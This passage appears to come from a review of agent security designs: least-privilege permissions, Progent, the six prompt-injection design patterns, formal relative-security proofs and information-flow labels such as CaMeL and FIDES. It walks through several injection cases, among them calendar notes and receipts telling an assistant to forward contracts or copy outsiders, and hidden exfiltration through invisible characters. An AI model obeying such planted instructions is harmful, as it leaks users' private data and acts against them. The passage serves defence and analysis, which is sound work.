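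The main measure weights permissions by risk. Four top-tier permissions count 3 points each, eight middle-tier ones count 2 and three bottom-tier ones count 1, so an agent with all 15 has an exposure of 12 + 16 + 3 = 31. The score is the share of those 31 points that the system removes. For example, a task that needs one top-tier permission and two bottom-tier ones requires 5 of the 31 points.

| What the agent receives | Weight granted | Exposure removed | Can it finish the task? |
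|---|---|---|---|
| All 15 permissions | 31 | 0% | Yes |
| Exactly the three it needs | 5 | 26/31 = 83.9% | Yes |
| Those three and one middle-tier extra | 7 | 24/31 = 77.4% | Yes |
| Only the two bottom-tier ones | 2 | 29/31 = 93.5% | No |
| Nothing | 0 | 100% | No |

The third row contains an over-grant, a permission the task doesn't need, and the score falls as it should. The fourth row contains an under-grant, a needed permission that the system has withheld. The score rises by almost ten points even though the agent can no longer do its job. Removing a permission always raises the score, whether or not the task needs it, so Noyan says to read the score together with the share of tasks that lost a permission they needed.

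| Layers in use | Weighted exposure removed | Tasks missing a needed permission |
|---|---|---|
| Role ceiling | 27.9% | 2% |
| Task classifier | 84.2% | 21% |
| Ceiling and classifier | 84.4% | 23% |
| Ceiling, classifier and prohibitions | 84.4% | 23% |

Adding the classifier to the role ceiling tripled the share of exposure removed, from 27.9% to 84.4%. Few companies give an agent every permission, so the ceiling is the more realistic baseline, and from there the classifier removed 78.3% of the remaining exposure. Adding the ceiling to the classifier removed only another 0.2 percentage points, all from two tasks in which the ceiling mistakenly removed a permission the task needed.

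A score of 84.4% is also close to the best possible, because the tasks required most of the access they kept. The average task kept 4.85 of the 31 points, of which only 0.53 were surplus.

The system failed on availability. Before the experiments, Noyan decided that a system fit for real use must have fewer than 10% of tasks lose a needed permission and a precision (the share of granted permissions that were correct, averaged across the types) of at least 0.90. The classifier met the precision requirement with 0.915, but 21% of tasks lost at least one permission they needed, or 23% with the ceiling in place. Because the sample had only 100 tasks, the true rate for the full system could be anywhere from roughly 16% to 32%, which is still above the limit. In a real company, those tasks would stop, or the agent would have to ask someone for more access.

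Noyan also tested Claude Haiku 4.5, a small general-purpose model from Anthropic, in place of the trained classifier, with six examples and no special training. At its standard setting, Haiku 4.5 under-granted on 11% of tasks and over-granted on 42%. The trained classifier under-granted on 21% and over-granted on 23% at the same setting. Neither model met both parts of the standard at any setting. Haiku 4.5 dates from 2025, and stronger models might do better on both.

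Noyan doubts that a better classifier would help much and blames the list of permissions instead. "Read the database" covers both harmless and highly sensitive records, and it accounted for 34% of the weighted surplus. Splitting that permission by sensitivity would probably reduce over-grants. It is less clear that it would fix under-grants, which matter most here, because they were spread almost evenly over twelve permissions. In Noyan's hypothetical evaluation, using a fixed list of approved cases to make decisions about external email cut under-grants from 21% to 18%.

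The prohibitions had no effect when the trained classifier was on, because the classifier never granted a forbidden pair of permissions. They are a backup, so Noyan also tested them with the classifier off and each agent holding every permission its department's ceiling allowed. The prohibitions then reduced the ceilings of three departments by 11.5% to 13.6%, but blocked between 6% and 31% of those departments' legitimate tasks. In 56 of the 57 blocked tasks, the agent held both permissions in a forbidden pair but never used both. Checking for forbidden pairs when an agent uses its permissions would avoid most of these blocks, but Noyan has not tested such a check.

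None of the 600 tasks was an attack, so the 84.4% measures how much access was removed, not how many attacks were stopped. Noyan expects the classifier to grant too much access if an attacker alters the task description. The classifier's job is also easier at the imaginary company than it would be elsewhere. The same six departments appear in the training and test data, so the classifier may have learned each department's habits. A real employee might also write a vaguer request, such as "same as last month, but for Leeds".

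### Permissions that change during the task

Permissions fixed at the start fail when the request doesn't reveal what the work involves. *Progent* (Shi, He et al., 2025) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to carry out the to-do list in an email from Alice. Nobody can tell which tools that requires until the agent opens the email.

Progent sits between the agent and its tools and checks every tool call against a list of rules. Each rule allows or forbids a tool and can set conditions on the call's arguments, such as "allow Slack messages if the recipient is alice". Rules that forbid take priority, and Progent blocks any call that no rule allows. When it blocks a call, it returns an error message so the agent can try another way to finish the task. An organisation can add permanent rules that no task can override, which serve the same purpose as a role ceiling.

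A language model writes the first rules from the user's request and proposes changes as the agent learns more. An attacker might manipulate that model, so ordinary software checks its proposals. If A(P) is the set of tool calls that the current rules P allow, new rules P′ take effect automatically only when

A(P′) ⊆ A(P)

which means that they allow nothing the old rules didn't. A constraint solver, a program that settles logical questions of this kind exactly, makes the comparison. Anything else is an expansion and needs approval.

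In the example, the first rule allows only a search for Alice's email. The email contains a request for a summary of recent messages, to be posted to the user's own Slack account. The model proposes allowing three more tools, which someone has to approve because it expands the agent's permissions. The agent then looks up the user's Slack name, and the model narrows the rule to messages sent to that name, which takes effect at once. One of the messages the agent reads for the summary contains an injected instruction to forward the inbox to an outsider. Even if the injection leads the model to propose an email tool, that would be another expansion, and the approver can refuse it.

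Progent guarantees that the agent's permissions can't grow without approval, so the guarantee's value depends on the approver. The legitimate request for Slack and the malicious request for email both come from text that the agent has just read, and the solver can't tell them apart. Progent can refuse all expansions, accept them all, follow rules for each tool, or ask a person. Only 6% of the proposed changes in one set of tests were expansions, so a person would have few to review. But Progent accepted every expansion automatically in the main benchmark runs, where it cut attack success from 39.9% to 1.0%. That reduction therefore came from the rules that the model wrote, not from the approval requirement.

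Shi and colleagues also exclude attacks that stay within the permissions a task needs. If the task is to choose a supplier and place an order, an attacker can try to make the agent choose the wrong supplier, and every tool call will look normal. Progent also doesn't check the agent's written answers, so it would miss a false payment date in a summary.

### How agents ask users for permission

In most products, users approve the agent's actions, but they have less control than the settings suggest. *How Agents Ask for Permission* (Michael and Roesner, 2026) reviewed 21 proposed permission systems and tried out five commercial agents in May and June 2026. It found that the commercial agents tended either to ask about nearly everything or to decide for the user with little explanation.

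ChatGPT's chat mode asked for approval of every action that its permission settings covered, and there was apparently no way to approve any in advance. Its agent mode, which operates a remote browser, offered no such settings and opened Gmail without asking. Under its "Needs approval" setting, the Claude chatbot sometimes let a language model approve an action, such as creating a draft email, without telling the user. Users could not turn this off without blocking the tool. OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, presented the same feature more openly. Its automatic reviewer was off by default, and users could switch it on or off for a whole session but not for individual tools.

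Permissions could also outlast the task. A user who had given Claude Cowork, Anthropic's desktop agent, access to a folder found no way to withdraw it inside the app. New sessions started without the permission, but old sessions kept it, and anyone using the app could reopen them. These products change quickly, so some details may already be out of date.

Of the 21 academic systems, twelve require little effort from users, eleven define their policies in a formal language, and twelve enforce their policies with fixed code or the user's own decisions instead of a model's judgement, but none does all three. Only six clearly let users change or withdraw a permission later, which most of the commercial agents allow.

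Granting agents too few permissions adds to the approval fatigue that the Coalition for Secure AI warns about. If a company's agents handle 1,000 tasks a day and 23% of those tasks lack a needed permission, staff will face at least 230 requests a day for access the agents should already have had. A classifier that withholds too much could therefore make the company less secure.

In *AI Security Priorities*, Gekker, Steratore and colleagues (2026) asked experts from industry, government and civil society to rate possible areas of work in AI security. Permission frameworks for agents ranked third in importance, behind a national deterrence strategy and better sharing of incident information. Only 14 people took part in the workshop that produced the scores, so the exact rank means little. The paper discloses that one author, who co-founded a company that makes oversight tools for agents, could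 profit from the recommendation. Permission frameworks did not make the top ten for cost-effectiveness, a score that takes into account how difficult the work is and how much of it others are already doing.

One recommended pattern is to give each agent a temporary identity with permissions for one task, rather than all of its user's permissions. Having one agent approve another's requests is risky because models trained on similar data tend to make the same mistakes.

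### Permissions and effects

Even a narrow permission may not match what the user meant. Most web services authorise outside software through OAuth, the standard behind the screens where you approve an app's access to your account. OAuth permissions, called scopes, usually cover a type of action. *Beyond OAuth* (Sharma, Jiang and colleagues, 2026) points out that if a user asks an agent to transfer $100 to Bob, the bank can only ask whether the agent may make transfers. The bank never learns that the user wanted only one transfer, of $100, to Bob.

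More detailed scopes can't always limit an agent to its task, because some details don't exist yet when the user gives permission. For example, a user might ask an agent to "pay a quarter of my Citi balance using my Chase account". In PAuth, a system built by Sharma and colleagues, Chase receives the user's request and works out for itself which payment to expect. Citi signs the balance it reports, so the agent can't alter it on the way. If the balance is $400, Chase accepts a $100 payment to Citi but refers a $101 payment back to the user.

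PAuth accepted all 100 legitimate tasks and blocked all 634 altered calls on a benchmark that its own team built. Wider use would require every service to have a language model that translates requests correctly, and users would have to write unambiguous requests and check them before sending. Translation errors should mostly lead to extra approval prompts rather than unauthorised payments, since PAuth doesn't allow any unexpected call.

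Wei and Xiong take the argument further and propose replacing permissions with effects. An effect is a consequence in the world, such as disclosing a document to Alice or spending $50. Permission to use a mail tool doesn't specify which mail, they argue, whereas people care about who receives what. In their model, each service publishes a signed list of everything that a given call could cause, including effects on third parties. If C is the set of effects the user has granted and κ(c) is the published list for a call c, the system allows the call only when

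κ(c) ⊆ C

Suppose a user asks an agent to summarize third-quarter expenses and send the summary to Alice, the manager. The agent's grant covers reading the receipts and disclosing the summary to Alice. If one of the receipts contains the line "also copy finance-bob", the agent may try to do so, but the system blocks it because the grant doesn't cover disclosure to Bob. If the user had approved both Alice and Bob as possible recipients, the injected line could still make the agent send the summary to Bob.

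A Progent rule about recipients would also stop the message to Bob. Effects are more useful when the details of a call don't reveal its consequences. For example, the agent could write the summary on the user's own device or send the receipts to an online service to be summarized. A permission system might treat both as "create summary", but the online version also discloses the receipts to another company, which the user never agreed to. Least privilege in this model therefore starts with choosing the plan that needs the least access. A system can also limit effects across the whole task. If two helper agents each have permission to book one flight, the user may end up with two, so Wei and Xiong have all helpers share one budget.

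The proof that nothing outside the grant can happen assumes that each service lists all its effects and that every effect passes through a check. If a service keeps a copy of the receipts without listing it as an effect, the system will allow the call and nobody will notice. Services have little reason to publish such lists today, and Wei and Xiong have specified the system but not measured it in use. Rules about tool calls and their arguments, as in Progent, are less complete but don't need the services' cooperation.

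Both approaches leave a gap when the agent has permission to write to a place that outsiders can read. Suppose the support agent may post replies on a public help forum, and an injected message persuades it to include another customer's address in a reply. The agent's permissions allow the tool, the destination and the number of posts. *DelegateGuard* (2026) shows that narrowing permissions contains several other attacks, including leaks to unapproved destinations and the reuse of revoked credentials. But it also proves that a permission check that ignores the content and quantity of what the agent sends cannot prevent this kind of leak. To stop the reply, the system would have to inspect its content or track where the address came from.

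## Six designs that keep untrusted text from choosing actions

Narrow permissions limit the damage an agent can do, but the model still decides how to use them after reading text that strangers wrote. In June 2025, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues published six designs that keep such text from choosing the agent's actions. All six apply the rule that untrusted input, once read, must not trigger an action that harms the system or its surroundings. At a minimum, the agent must then be unable to use any tool that could corrupt or disclose protected data. Its written output must also be safe to pass on, with no links that carry data to an attacker and no text that would manipulate another agent later.

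The rule prevents agents from doing some tasks. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues accept this limit in each design because they doubt that a general-purpose agent can offer reliable guarantees with current language models.

One request shows how most of the designs work. A user tells an assistant to "send today's schedule to my boss John Doe". Outsiders can send the user calendar invitations, so the calendar is untrusted content. Suppose an attacker sends a 3 p.m. invitation with a note instructing the assistant to search the mailbox for contracts and forward them to an outside address. An ordinary agent that reads the note may well start searching.

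### Action-selector: a fixed menu

In the action-selector pattern, the model receives the user's request and picks an action from a list that developers wrote in advance. Ordinary software carries out the action and shows the result to the user. The model never sees the result, so nothing in it can influence the model. A shop's chatbot might have three actions: link to the customer's last order, open the password settings, and open the payment settings. Developers can also leave blanks in an action for the model to fill in, such as the product name in a database query.

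A company could put "email today's calendar to my manager" on the menu. Software would copy the entries into a message, including the attacker's note under the 3 p.m. meeting. The note could contain a phishing link, but it couldn't change the other entries. If the manager also uses an AI assistant, the note might still hijack that assistant.

Anyone who writes the request, including an attacker who gets the user to paste in a hostile prompt, can choose any action on the action-selector's list. Each action therefore has to be safe for anyone who can reach the bot to trigger. The pattern also rules out any task that requires the model to read something before it acts, such as summarising an email or answering a question about a web page.

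### Plan-then-execute: the steps come first

Plan-then-execute lets the agent use what its tools return. The model turns the request into a fixed list of tool calls before the agent fetches anything. For the schedule request, the plan is to read today's calendar, then send an email to john.doe@company.com with the body left blank. Software runs the steps in order, and a model fills in the body after reading the calendar.

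The attacker's note can't add a mailbox search or redirect the email, because the plan already sets the steps and the address. But the model writes the body after reading the note, so the attacker can change the body in any way. The boss might receive, from the employee's real account, a schedule with a meeting missing or a request to approve a payment before noon.

Security engineers call this kind of protection control-flow integrity. It means an attacker can't change which operations run or in what order, but it doesn't protect the values passed between them. *SPA* (2026) points out that an attack on those values needs no hidden instruction. If the plan is to pay the account number on an invoice, the attacker only has to send an invoice with the wrong number.

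The schedule's recipient is safe because the request determined it. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues also discuss a request to tell "my regular collaborators" about a vacation. The assistant has to work out who they are, perhaps from how often people appear in recent meetings and emails. An outsider who sends enough invitations could be included, even though the plan never changes.

The planner also has to be free of untrusted text when it writes the plan. Its prompt usually includes the names and descriptions of the available tools, which *SPA* treats as a separate way in for attackers. A tool from an unknown supplier could carry an injection in its description, and the planner would read it before writing the plan. Text that the user pastes into the request also reaches the planner.

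The pattern rules out tasks in which the next step depends on the result of the previous one. For example, an agent that answers questions from a database often looks at its first results and then writes a better query, but with a fixed plan it gets only one attempt.

### Map-reduce: one reader for each item

With a fixed plan, one hostile calendar entry can corrupt the whole email because a single model reads all the entries together. The map-reduce pattern gives each item to a separate model call that has no tools (the "map" step) and combines the answers (the "reduce" step). The answers must fit a strict format, such as yes or no, a number, or one category from a list. Software can enforce this by restricting which tokens the model may produce. The reduce step can be ordinary code, or a model with tools if the answers cannot contain instructions.

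For the schedule, a separate model call for each entry could return "meeting", "travel" or "private", and code could build the email from the times and those labels. The hostile invitation could cause its own entry to be mislabelled, but it couldn't change any other line. The email would be safer but less useful, because the boss would learn that there is a meeting at 3 p.m. but not what it is about.

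Beurer-Kellner and colleagues give the example of a user who wants the month's invoices emailed to the accounting department. An isolated model checks each file and answers whether it is an invoice, and then another model writes and sends the email. They conclude that the most an attacker can do with a hostile file is get it accepted as an invoice, which submitting a real invoice would also achieve. That is true only if the second model attaches the files without reading their contents or their names, since attackers can choose both.

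Map-reduce suits searching, sorting and scoring, but not tasks where a model has to read several items together, such as explaining how two contracts differ.

### Dual model: separating reading from acting

Map-reduce is a special case of an older, more general design that the programmer Simon Willison proposed in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (2023). The design splits an assistant between two language models. The privileged model takes the user's instructions and can use tools, but never reads untrusted content. The quarantined model reads untrusted content but has no tools, and the design assumes that it could turn hostile at any moment. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) compares this to separation of duty, the principle behind having one employee request a payment and another approve it.

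A third component, the controller, is ordinary software that passes values between the two models under placeholder names, so the privileged model never receives the schedule's text. The privileged model first issues an instruction to fetch today's calendar, and the controller stores the entries as $VAR1. The next instruction is to tidy $VAR1. The controller sends the entries to the quarantined model, stores its output as $VAR2, and tells the privileged model only that the work is done. The privileged model then issues an instruction to email $VAR2 to John Doe, and the controller inserts the text as it sends the message.

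The privileged model can safely receive the quarantined model's answer only if software can verify that the answer contains no instructions, for example by checking that it is one of a fixed set of categories. Willison calls it "absolutely crucial" that no other output gets through. Defences that use the pattern's name don't always follow this rule. *ORBIT* (2026), a framework for testing the safety of groups of agents, includes a "dual-LLM" defence in which the quarantined model summarises each tool result and the privileged model reads the summary. An injection that survives the summary therefore reaches the model with the tools, so a poor test result for that defence would be weak evidence about Willison's design.

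Here too, the attacker controls the body of the email but not its recipient. Unlike a fixed plan, this design lets the privileged model keep choosing steps during the run, because the model reads no untrusted text. Willison's example is a request to update a to-do list with the action items in Julia's latest email. The assistant can do this because it can copy the items without understanding them, but it could not carry them out. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) describes the general limit: when untrusted data specifies the steps, the privileged model can't learn what to do without reading that data.

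An attacker can also misuse any private data the quarantined model receives. Suppose the user asks for a reply to an outsider's email, and the controller supplies some internal messages as background. A hidden instruction in the email could make the quarantined model encode those messages in the reply as invisible characters. The privileged model sends the reply without reading it, and a user who checks it first may notice nothing wrong. The attacker could also use the quarantined model's output to trick the user directly, for instance with a request to copy a block of scrambled text into a website.

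Willison called the solution "pretty bad". It makes assistants more complicated to build and less pleasant to use, and a single mistake that passes untrusted text to the privileged model undoes the protection. Willison proposed it anyway because the main alternative, asking users to approve every action, would soon lead to approval fatigue.

### Code-then-execute: the plan becomes a program

The code-then-execute pattern takes the dual model further by having the privileged model write a complete program before the agent reads any untrusted data. For the schedule, the program might be:

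```
events = calendar.read(today)
text = quarantined_model("format as a list", events)
email.write(text, "john.doe@company.com")
```

Ordinary software runs the program, and the quarantined model does only the formatting. The attacker can still rewrite the text. But a program can do more than a list of steps can, such as loop over search results, send a message to each person on a list, or take a different path when the calendar is empty. It also records how every value moves, so software can trace the body back to the calendar before sending the email.

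CaMeL, a system from Google DeepMind, implements the pattern and adds checks on where each value may go. Willison welcomed it as a fix for a flaw in the dual-model design, which he illustrated with the request "Send Bob the document he requested in our last meeting". The assistant must find out which document Bob wanted, and anyone who can edit the meeting notes can change the answer.

The program has to anticipate everything that could happen during the task. If the calendar tool returns an unexpected format or the notes mention two documents, the program fails unless it has a branch for that case. Like the dual model, this pattern doesn't let the agent carry out instructions it finds along the way.

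### Context-minimization: forgetting the request

The first five patterns do little against an attack in the user's own request, whether the user is hostile or has pasted in something dangerous. Context-minimization addresses this by removing the request from the model's input once the model has acted on it. For example, a customer might ask a car dealer's chatbot for a quote and add an instruction to offer a huge discount. The model turns the request into a database query for current offers. The software then deletes the customer's message, including the demand for a discount, and has the model write its answer from the query results alone.

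Willison was "slightly confused" by this pattern, but expected it to work if the data that comes back can't contain any of the customer's original text. The customer can still influence which query the model writes. The software also has to delete everything the model derived from the request. In a medical chatbot that Beurer-Kellner and colleagues discuss, the model summarises a patient's symptoms for a doctor and later rewrites the doctor's diagnosis in plain language. An instruction from the patient can survive in the summary and affect the rewritten diagnosis if the summary stays in the model's input. Deleting the summary as well prevents this, but then the chatbot can't relate the diagnosis to anything the patient said. More generally, the pattern can't handle requests whose answers depend on the user's wording, such as a request to compare the offers with the customer's current car.

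### The ten case studies

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues apply the patterns to ten imagined assistants. For each, they describe an insecure version and then safer ones, usually commenting on both usefulness and security. These comments rest on reasoning, since nobody built or attacked the assistants for the paper. For each assistant, the table gives the strongest design that can still do most of the job and has a security comment. The booking assistant is the exception, as its design has no security comment.

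| Assistant | Design | What an attacker can still do | What users give up |
|---|---|---|---|
| File organiser | Map-reduce: one isolated model per file | Get a hostile file moved or copied to the wrong place | Tasks that don't divide by file |
| Database analyst | Plan-then-execute, with generated code in a sandbox | Attack through the question; extract data through the analysis | Refining a query after seeing results |
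| Email and calendar assistant | Dual model | Tamper with drafts, for instance to hide private data in them | Little, for most requests |
| Customer service chatbot | Action-selector with a list of allowed requests | Trigger the wrong allowed request, which is presumably safe | Reasonable requests that developers didn't foresee |
| Booking assistant | Dual model or code-then-execute | No assessment | No assessment |
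| Product recommender | Map-reduce: one isolated model per review | Write a review that claims every merit | Summaries outside the chosen categories |
| CV screener | Map-reduce for ranking, dual model for summaries | Raise a CV's own ranking; misstate experience | Time spent getting a good summary template |
| Medication leaflet chatbot | Context-minimization: shows only passages from the leaflet | Make the model leave out relevant passages, such as warnings | Flexible answers |
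| Medical diagnosis chatbot | Context-minimization, with symptoms in a fixed form | Nothing in the symptom summary | Symptoms that don't fit the form |
| Coding assistant | Dual model: outside documentation becomes a strict list of functions | Slip an injection through the format, which is "unlikely" | Explanations and code examples |

The file organiser is the best case for comparing designs because it covers five of them. A user asks the assistant to find all tax-related PDF files and move them into a folder called Taxes. The attacker controls the name or contents of at least one file and wants to run harmful commands or steal data.

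The first version gives the model a command line. The model can do every task, but any file it reads could make it run any command, and it might delete files by mistake even without an attack. The second version asks the user to confirm each command. Most people can't judge these commands, and an attacker can make a harmful one look innocent.

The third version is an action-selector with a set of ready-made commands. It is immune to injections in files because the model never reads the files. But it loses most of the benefit of a language model. For example, a command that moves every file with "tax" in its name would miss a scanned tax return called "scan0047.pdf".

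The fourth version commits to a plan that uses only two harmless-looking commands, one to find files and one to move them. Fixing the list of tools gives little protection if an attacker can choose the arguments of a powerful tool. Here, an injection could still make the model find sensitive files and move them to a public network drive. The schedule assistant's fixed plan kept an attacker from redirecting anything because it specified the recipient, whereas this plan leaves the choice of files and destination to the model.

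In the fifth version, a controlling model sends each file to an isolated model, which answers only whether the file is about tax. The controlling model receives the answers but never the contents, and the destination comes from the user's request. At worst, a hostile file ends up in the Taxes folder, which can still cause harm because an accountant might trust whatever is in there.

### How many designs keep a weakness

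Beurer-Kellner and colleagues report a remaining weakness in seven of the ten designs in the table. For the other three, they state no weakness in the diagnosis chatbot, describe one in the coding assistant that they consider unlikely, and do not comment on the security of the booking assistant's final designs.

Hirschberg (2026), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents Against Prompt Injection*, a post on the blog of the security company ARMO, counts eight cases rather than seven. The extra one is the booking assistant, for which the post acknowledges using an earlier design that only limits the agent to the user's own permissions. Seven is the better count because Beurer-Kellner and colleagues go on to propose two stronger designs. However, the total depends on which design represents each case. Choosing the action-selector version of the file organiser, which has no stated weakness,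 would lower it to six, but few people would want to use that version.

The seven weaknesses also differ in seriousness. A manipulated CV can raise its own ranking, as better writing would, but it can't push other candidates down by discrediting them. A tampered email draft could leak confidential plans. Users of the medication chatbot who suppress a warning are manipulating their own answers, so the danger is mostly a legal one for the company.

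Hirschberg explains that the weakness disappears when the output has no room for free text. Both the symptom form and the list of functions work this way. But even a strict format may leave some room. In the coding assistant, function names can have up to 30 characters, and Willison suggests that an attacker might use one like "run_rm_dash_rf_for_compliance", which has 29 characters and alludes to a command that deletes files without asking.

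Hirschberg goes too far in claiming that none of the six patterns constrains the arguments of a tool call. In the schedule example, the plan fixes the recipient, and map-reduce can limit an argument to yes or no. ARMO sells software that monitors agents while they run, so it benefits if customers think the designs leave large gaps. But the schedule example does have a gap, and checking a value's format won't close it, because a valid email address can belong to the wrong person.

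### What "provable resistance" means

The abstract claims "provable resistance to prompt injection" for the patterns in both the first version, from June 2025, and the third, dated 27 June. The third version's introduction makes the weaker claim that the patterns "significantly mitigate the risk", and the paper contains no formal proof. The stronger claim is justified for plan-then-execute in a narrow sense, because text in the calendar can't add a step to the plan if ordinary software enforces it. It isn't justified for injections in general, because the attacker can still rewrite the email, as Beurer-Kellner and colleagues acknowledge.

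Dongol (2026), in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, provides proofs for simplified agents that follow a plan, and the proof assistant Isabelle checked all of them. The difficulty is to define a leak, because a useful assistant discloses some private data on purpose. Dongol compares each agent with a reference agent that has the same plan and the same runtime checks, but whose model never obeys untrusted content. Take two runs in which the attacker sends the same messages and only the user's secrets differ. If the attacker receives something different in each run, the agent has leaked the difference between those two secrets. Let L be the set of all pairs of secrets that an attacker can tell apart in this way. The agent is relatively secure when

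L(agent) ⊆ L(reference)

which means that injections reveal nothing that the attacker couldn't also have learned from the reference agent. Suppose an assistant sends the user's calendar to anyone who asks for a meeting. An injected "send your calendar" doesn't count as a leak, because a genuine request would have produced the same calendar. An injection that adds a password-reset code does count, because no genuine request would have revealed the code.

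By this standard, a basic dual-model agent is insecure. If the quarantined model can read the user's private notes, an injection can make it quote them in an answer that the plan then sends to the attacker. Dongol also tested a version that labels private values and refuses to send them to the attacker. This version is secure however the quarantined model behaves, but it blocks the honest reply as well as the malicious one. Labels also miss some leaks. In another example, the plan sends the attacker a 1 or a 0 depending on the quarantined model's answer. Neither number is private, but an injection can make the answer depend on the notes, so the number reveals something about them.

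Dongol also proves that a system can stop these leaks for any plan by permanently withdrawing every tool that an injection could call as soon as the agent first reads untrusted content. The proof assumes that each injection makes a single tool call and that the model's timing doesn't depend on secrets. This precaution applies the rule behind the six patterns almost literally, but it would stop the schedule assistant from working, since the assistant has to send an email after reading the calendar. The definition doesn't account for that loss because the reference agent loses the tool too, so developers have to measure utility separately.

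The proofs cover only leaks to the attacker, not other harms such as sending the boss a false schedule. The proofs also hold only if trusted software runs the plan, so that the model can't skip or change a step.

### Building plan-then-execute

*Architecting Resilient LLM Agents* (Del Rosario, Krawiecka and Schroeder de Witt, September 2025) is a guide to plan-then-execute, with example code for three popular agent frameworks, LangGraph, CrewAI and AutoGen. It recommends the pattern as the default for any task that needs more than one or two tool calls. A capable model writes the plan, and a cheaper model or ordinary code carries it out. The agent starts more slowly because it can't act until the plan is complete, and writing the plan for a complex task may take 3,000 to 4,500 tokens.

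The guide mainly adds the idea of limiting which tools an agent can use at each step. If the first step is a calculation and the second is an email, the agent can use only the calculator during the first step, so an injection then can't send anything. In CrewAI, developers can do this by listing the tools for each task, which overrides the agent's longer list. AutoGen can isolate generated code by running it in a temporary container and deleting the container afterwards.

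Del Rosario and colleagues acknowledge that the pattern doesn't protect data that passes between steps. In their example, an agent finds a company report online and emails a summary to the chief executive, and an attacker who controls the website turns the summary into a phishing message. Their LangGraph code also protects less than the schedule example does. Each step of its plan has a task described in words and the name of one tool. For each step, the code creates a temporary agent with that tool and shows it the results of all earlier steps.

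In the schedule example, the second step would tell the temporary agent to email the schedule to John Doe and give it the email tool. The agent would read the calendar, including the attacker's note, and then write the whole tool call, including the address. The note could therefore redirect the email or cause the agent to send a second one. To keep the note from changing the recipient, the plan has to contain the address, and ordinary code has to put it into the call. The model that reads the calendar should supply only the body.

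The guide's advice on changing plans creates a larger problem. A fixed plan fails when a tool breaks or returns something unexpected, so Del Rosario and colleagues recommend adding a re-planner to production systems. After each step, this model receives the goal, the plan and the results so far, and it can write a new plan. They present it as a way to make agents more reliable and don't discuss its effect on security. If the results include the text of a web page, the page's author can influence the plan, which the pattern was supposed to prevent.

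Developers can keep some flexibility without this risk by giving the re-planner only fixed status messages, such as "succeeded" or "timed out". The guide also describes plans with built-in alternatives, such as trying a second search tool if the first fails. An attacker who can make the first tool fail can then choose between the alternatives, but can't add a new one.

For high-stakes work, Del Rosario and colleagues want an expert to approve the plan before the agent starts. They also cite a user study in which involving people in planning didn't consistently improve the plans, because a wrong plan presented confidently could mislead them. At this stage the expert can catch a bad plan but will usually miss an injection, because the schedule's plan is harmless when the expert sees it and the attacker's note only takes effect once the agent reads the calendar. A reviewer who sees the finished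 email just before it goes out is more likely to notice a strange request for payment, but not data hidden in invisible characters.

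## Tracking where data came from and where it may go

A fixed plan controls which steps an agent takes, but an attacker can still tamper with the values that pass between those steps. Data-flow labels limit where these values can go. Each label stays with its value during a run and records who could have written the value and who may read it. Ordinary software attaches the labels, combines them as the agent works, and checks them before each tool call. Computer scientists developed this method, known as information-flow control, in the 1970s.

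### How labels combine

Suppose the user who sent John Doe a schedule now wants one summary of today's calendar and a salary memo. John Doe may read the calendar but not the memo. When the agent combines two values x and y into a new value z, the software works out the label of z from theirs:

readers(z) = readers(x) ∩ readers(y)

writers(z) = writers(x) ∪ writers(y)

A person may read a value computed from two inputs only if they may read both inputs. Anyone who could have written either input could have influenced the result.

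| Value | Who may read it | Who could have written it |
|---|---|---|
| Calendar | User, John Doe | User, anyone who sends an invitation |
| Salary memo | User, HR | HR |
| Summary of both | User | User, HR, anyone who sends an invitation |

The summary can't go to John Doe, even if it leaves out the salaries. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) gives a model's output the combined label of everything the model read, because nobody can say precisely which parts of the input shaped it. The paper also mentions a more lenient method, which finds the messages that influenced an answer and regenerates the answer from those alone.

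Costa and colleagues describe two basic checks. The writer check allows a consequential tool call only if the decision to make it, and the details of the call, rest entirely on trusted text. The reader check allows the agent to send z only when

recipients ⊆ readers(z)

With only the reader check, an injection can still make the agent send mail, but only to people already allowed to read the contents. If the system uses only the writer check, the agent can send private data to an outsider, but untrusted text can't have prompted it to do so, so the user presumably wanted the data sent.

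In an ordinary agent, one model reads all the text in a single conversation, so after the first outside email the whole conversation counts as untrusted and these checks block every consequential tool call. CaMeL and Microsoft's FIDES avoid this by keeping untrusted text away from the main model, as in the dual-model design.

### CaMeL: labels on a program's variables

CaMeL starts from the code-then-execute pattern, in which the trusted model writes a program before the agent reads anything untrusted. For Willison's example of sending Bob the document he requested in the last meeting, the program might be:

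```
notes = files.read("last meeting")
name = quarantined_model("which document did Bob want?", notes)
doc = files.open(name)
email.write(doc, "bob@company.com")
```

The trusted model writes the plan from the user's request and the tool descriptions. It never sees the tools' results, so it has to know in advance what form each one will take. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) had to add that information to every tool description before their CaMeL agents completed a reasonable share of tasks.

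An interpreter, which is ordinary software, then runs the program line by line. It fetches the notes and stores them with a label that lists everyone who can edit them. The quarantined model, which has no tools, reads the notes and returns a document name, and the interpreter gives the name the same label. When the interpreter opens the document, it records who may read it. Before sending the email, it applies the email tool's policy, which can depend on the recipient, the document's label, and the labels of everything that led to the choice of document.

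Suppose an attacker edits the notes so that Bob appears to have asked for the company's acquisition plans. The quarantined model returns the wrong file name, so the program opens the wrong file. If Bob isn't among the file's permitted readers, the interpreter blocks the email. If he is, the email goes out and he gets a document he didn't ask for, but no data leaks.

Labels don't guarantee that the content is true. John Doe may read the user's calendar, so a schedule containing a false meeting passes the reader check. Banning untrusted text from all outgoing mail would block the false schedule, but also the real one. Even reasonable policies can keep a system from completing its tasks. *The LLMbda Calculus* reports that turning on CaMeL's policy checks halves the share of tasks the system completes in the banking part of AgentDojo, a benchmark of everyday agent tasks with attacks planted in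 the tool results.

### FIDES and its successor

FIDES, a system by Costa and colleagues, lets the main model choose one step at a time instead of writing the whole program first. When a tool returns a result, software compares the result's label with the conversation's. If adding the result would make the conversation less trusted or more private, the software stores it in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. Otherwise, the software adds the result to the conversation.

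If the user asks the system to summarize three emails and post the summary on Slack, the variables work as in the dual-model design, so the model chooses every step without reading untrusted text. The Slack message is still untrusted, but a policy can allow it as long as the recipient is trusted.

A request to carry out today's to-do list is harder, because the model has to know what is on it. The model can open the variable, but the conversation then becomes untrusted and later consequential calls fail the writer check. Or it can ask the quarantined model a question with a limited set of answers. FIDES records the answer's type in the label, so a policy could accept an untrusted yes or no, which carries at most one bit of information, and still reject an untrusted sentence.

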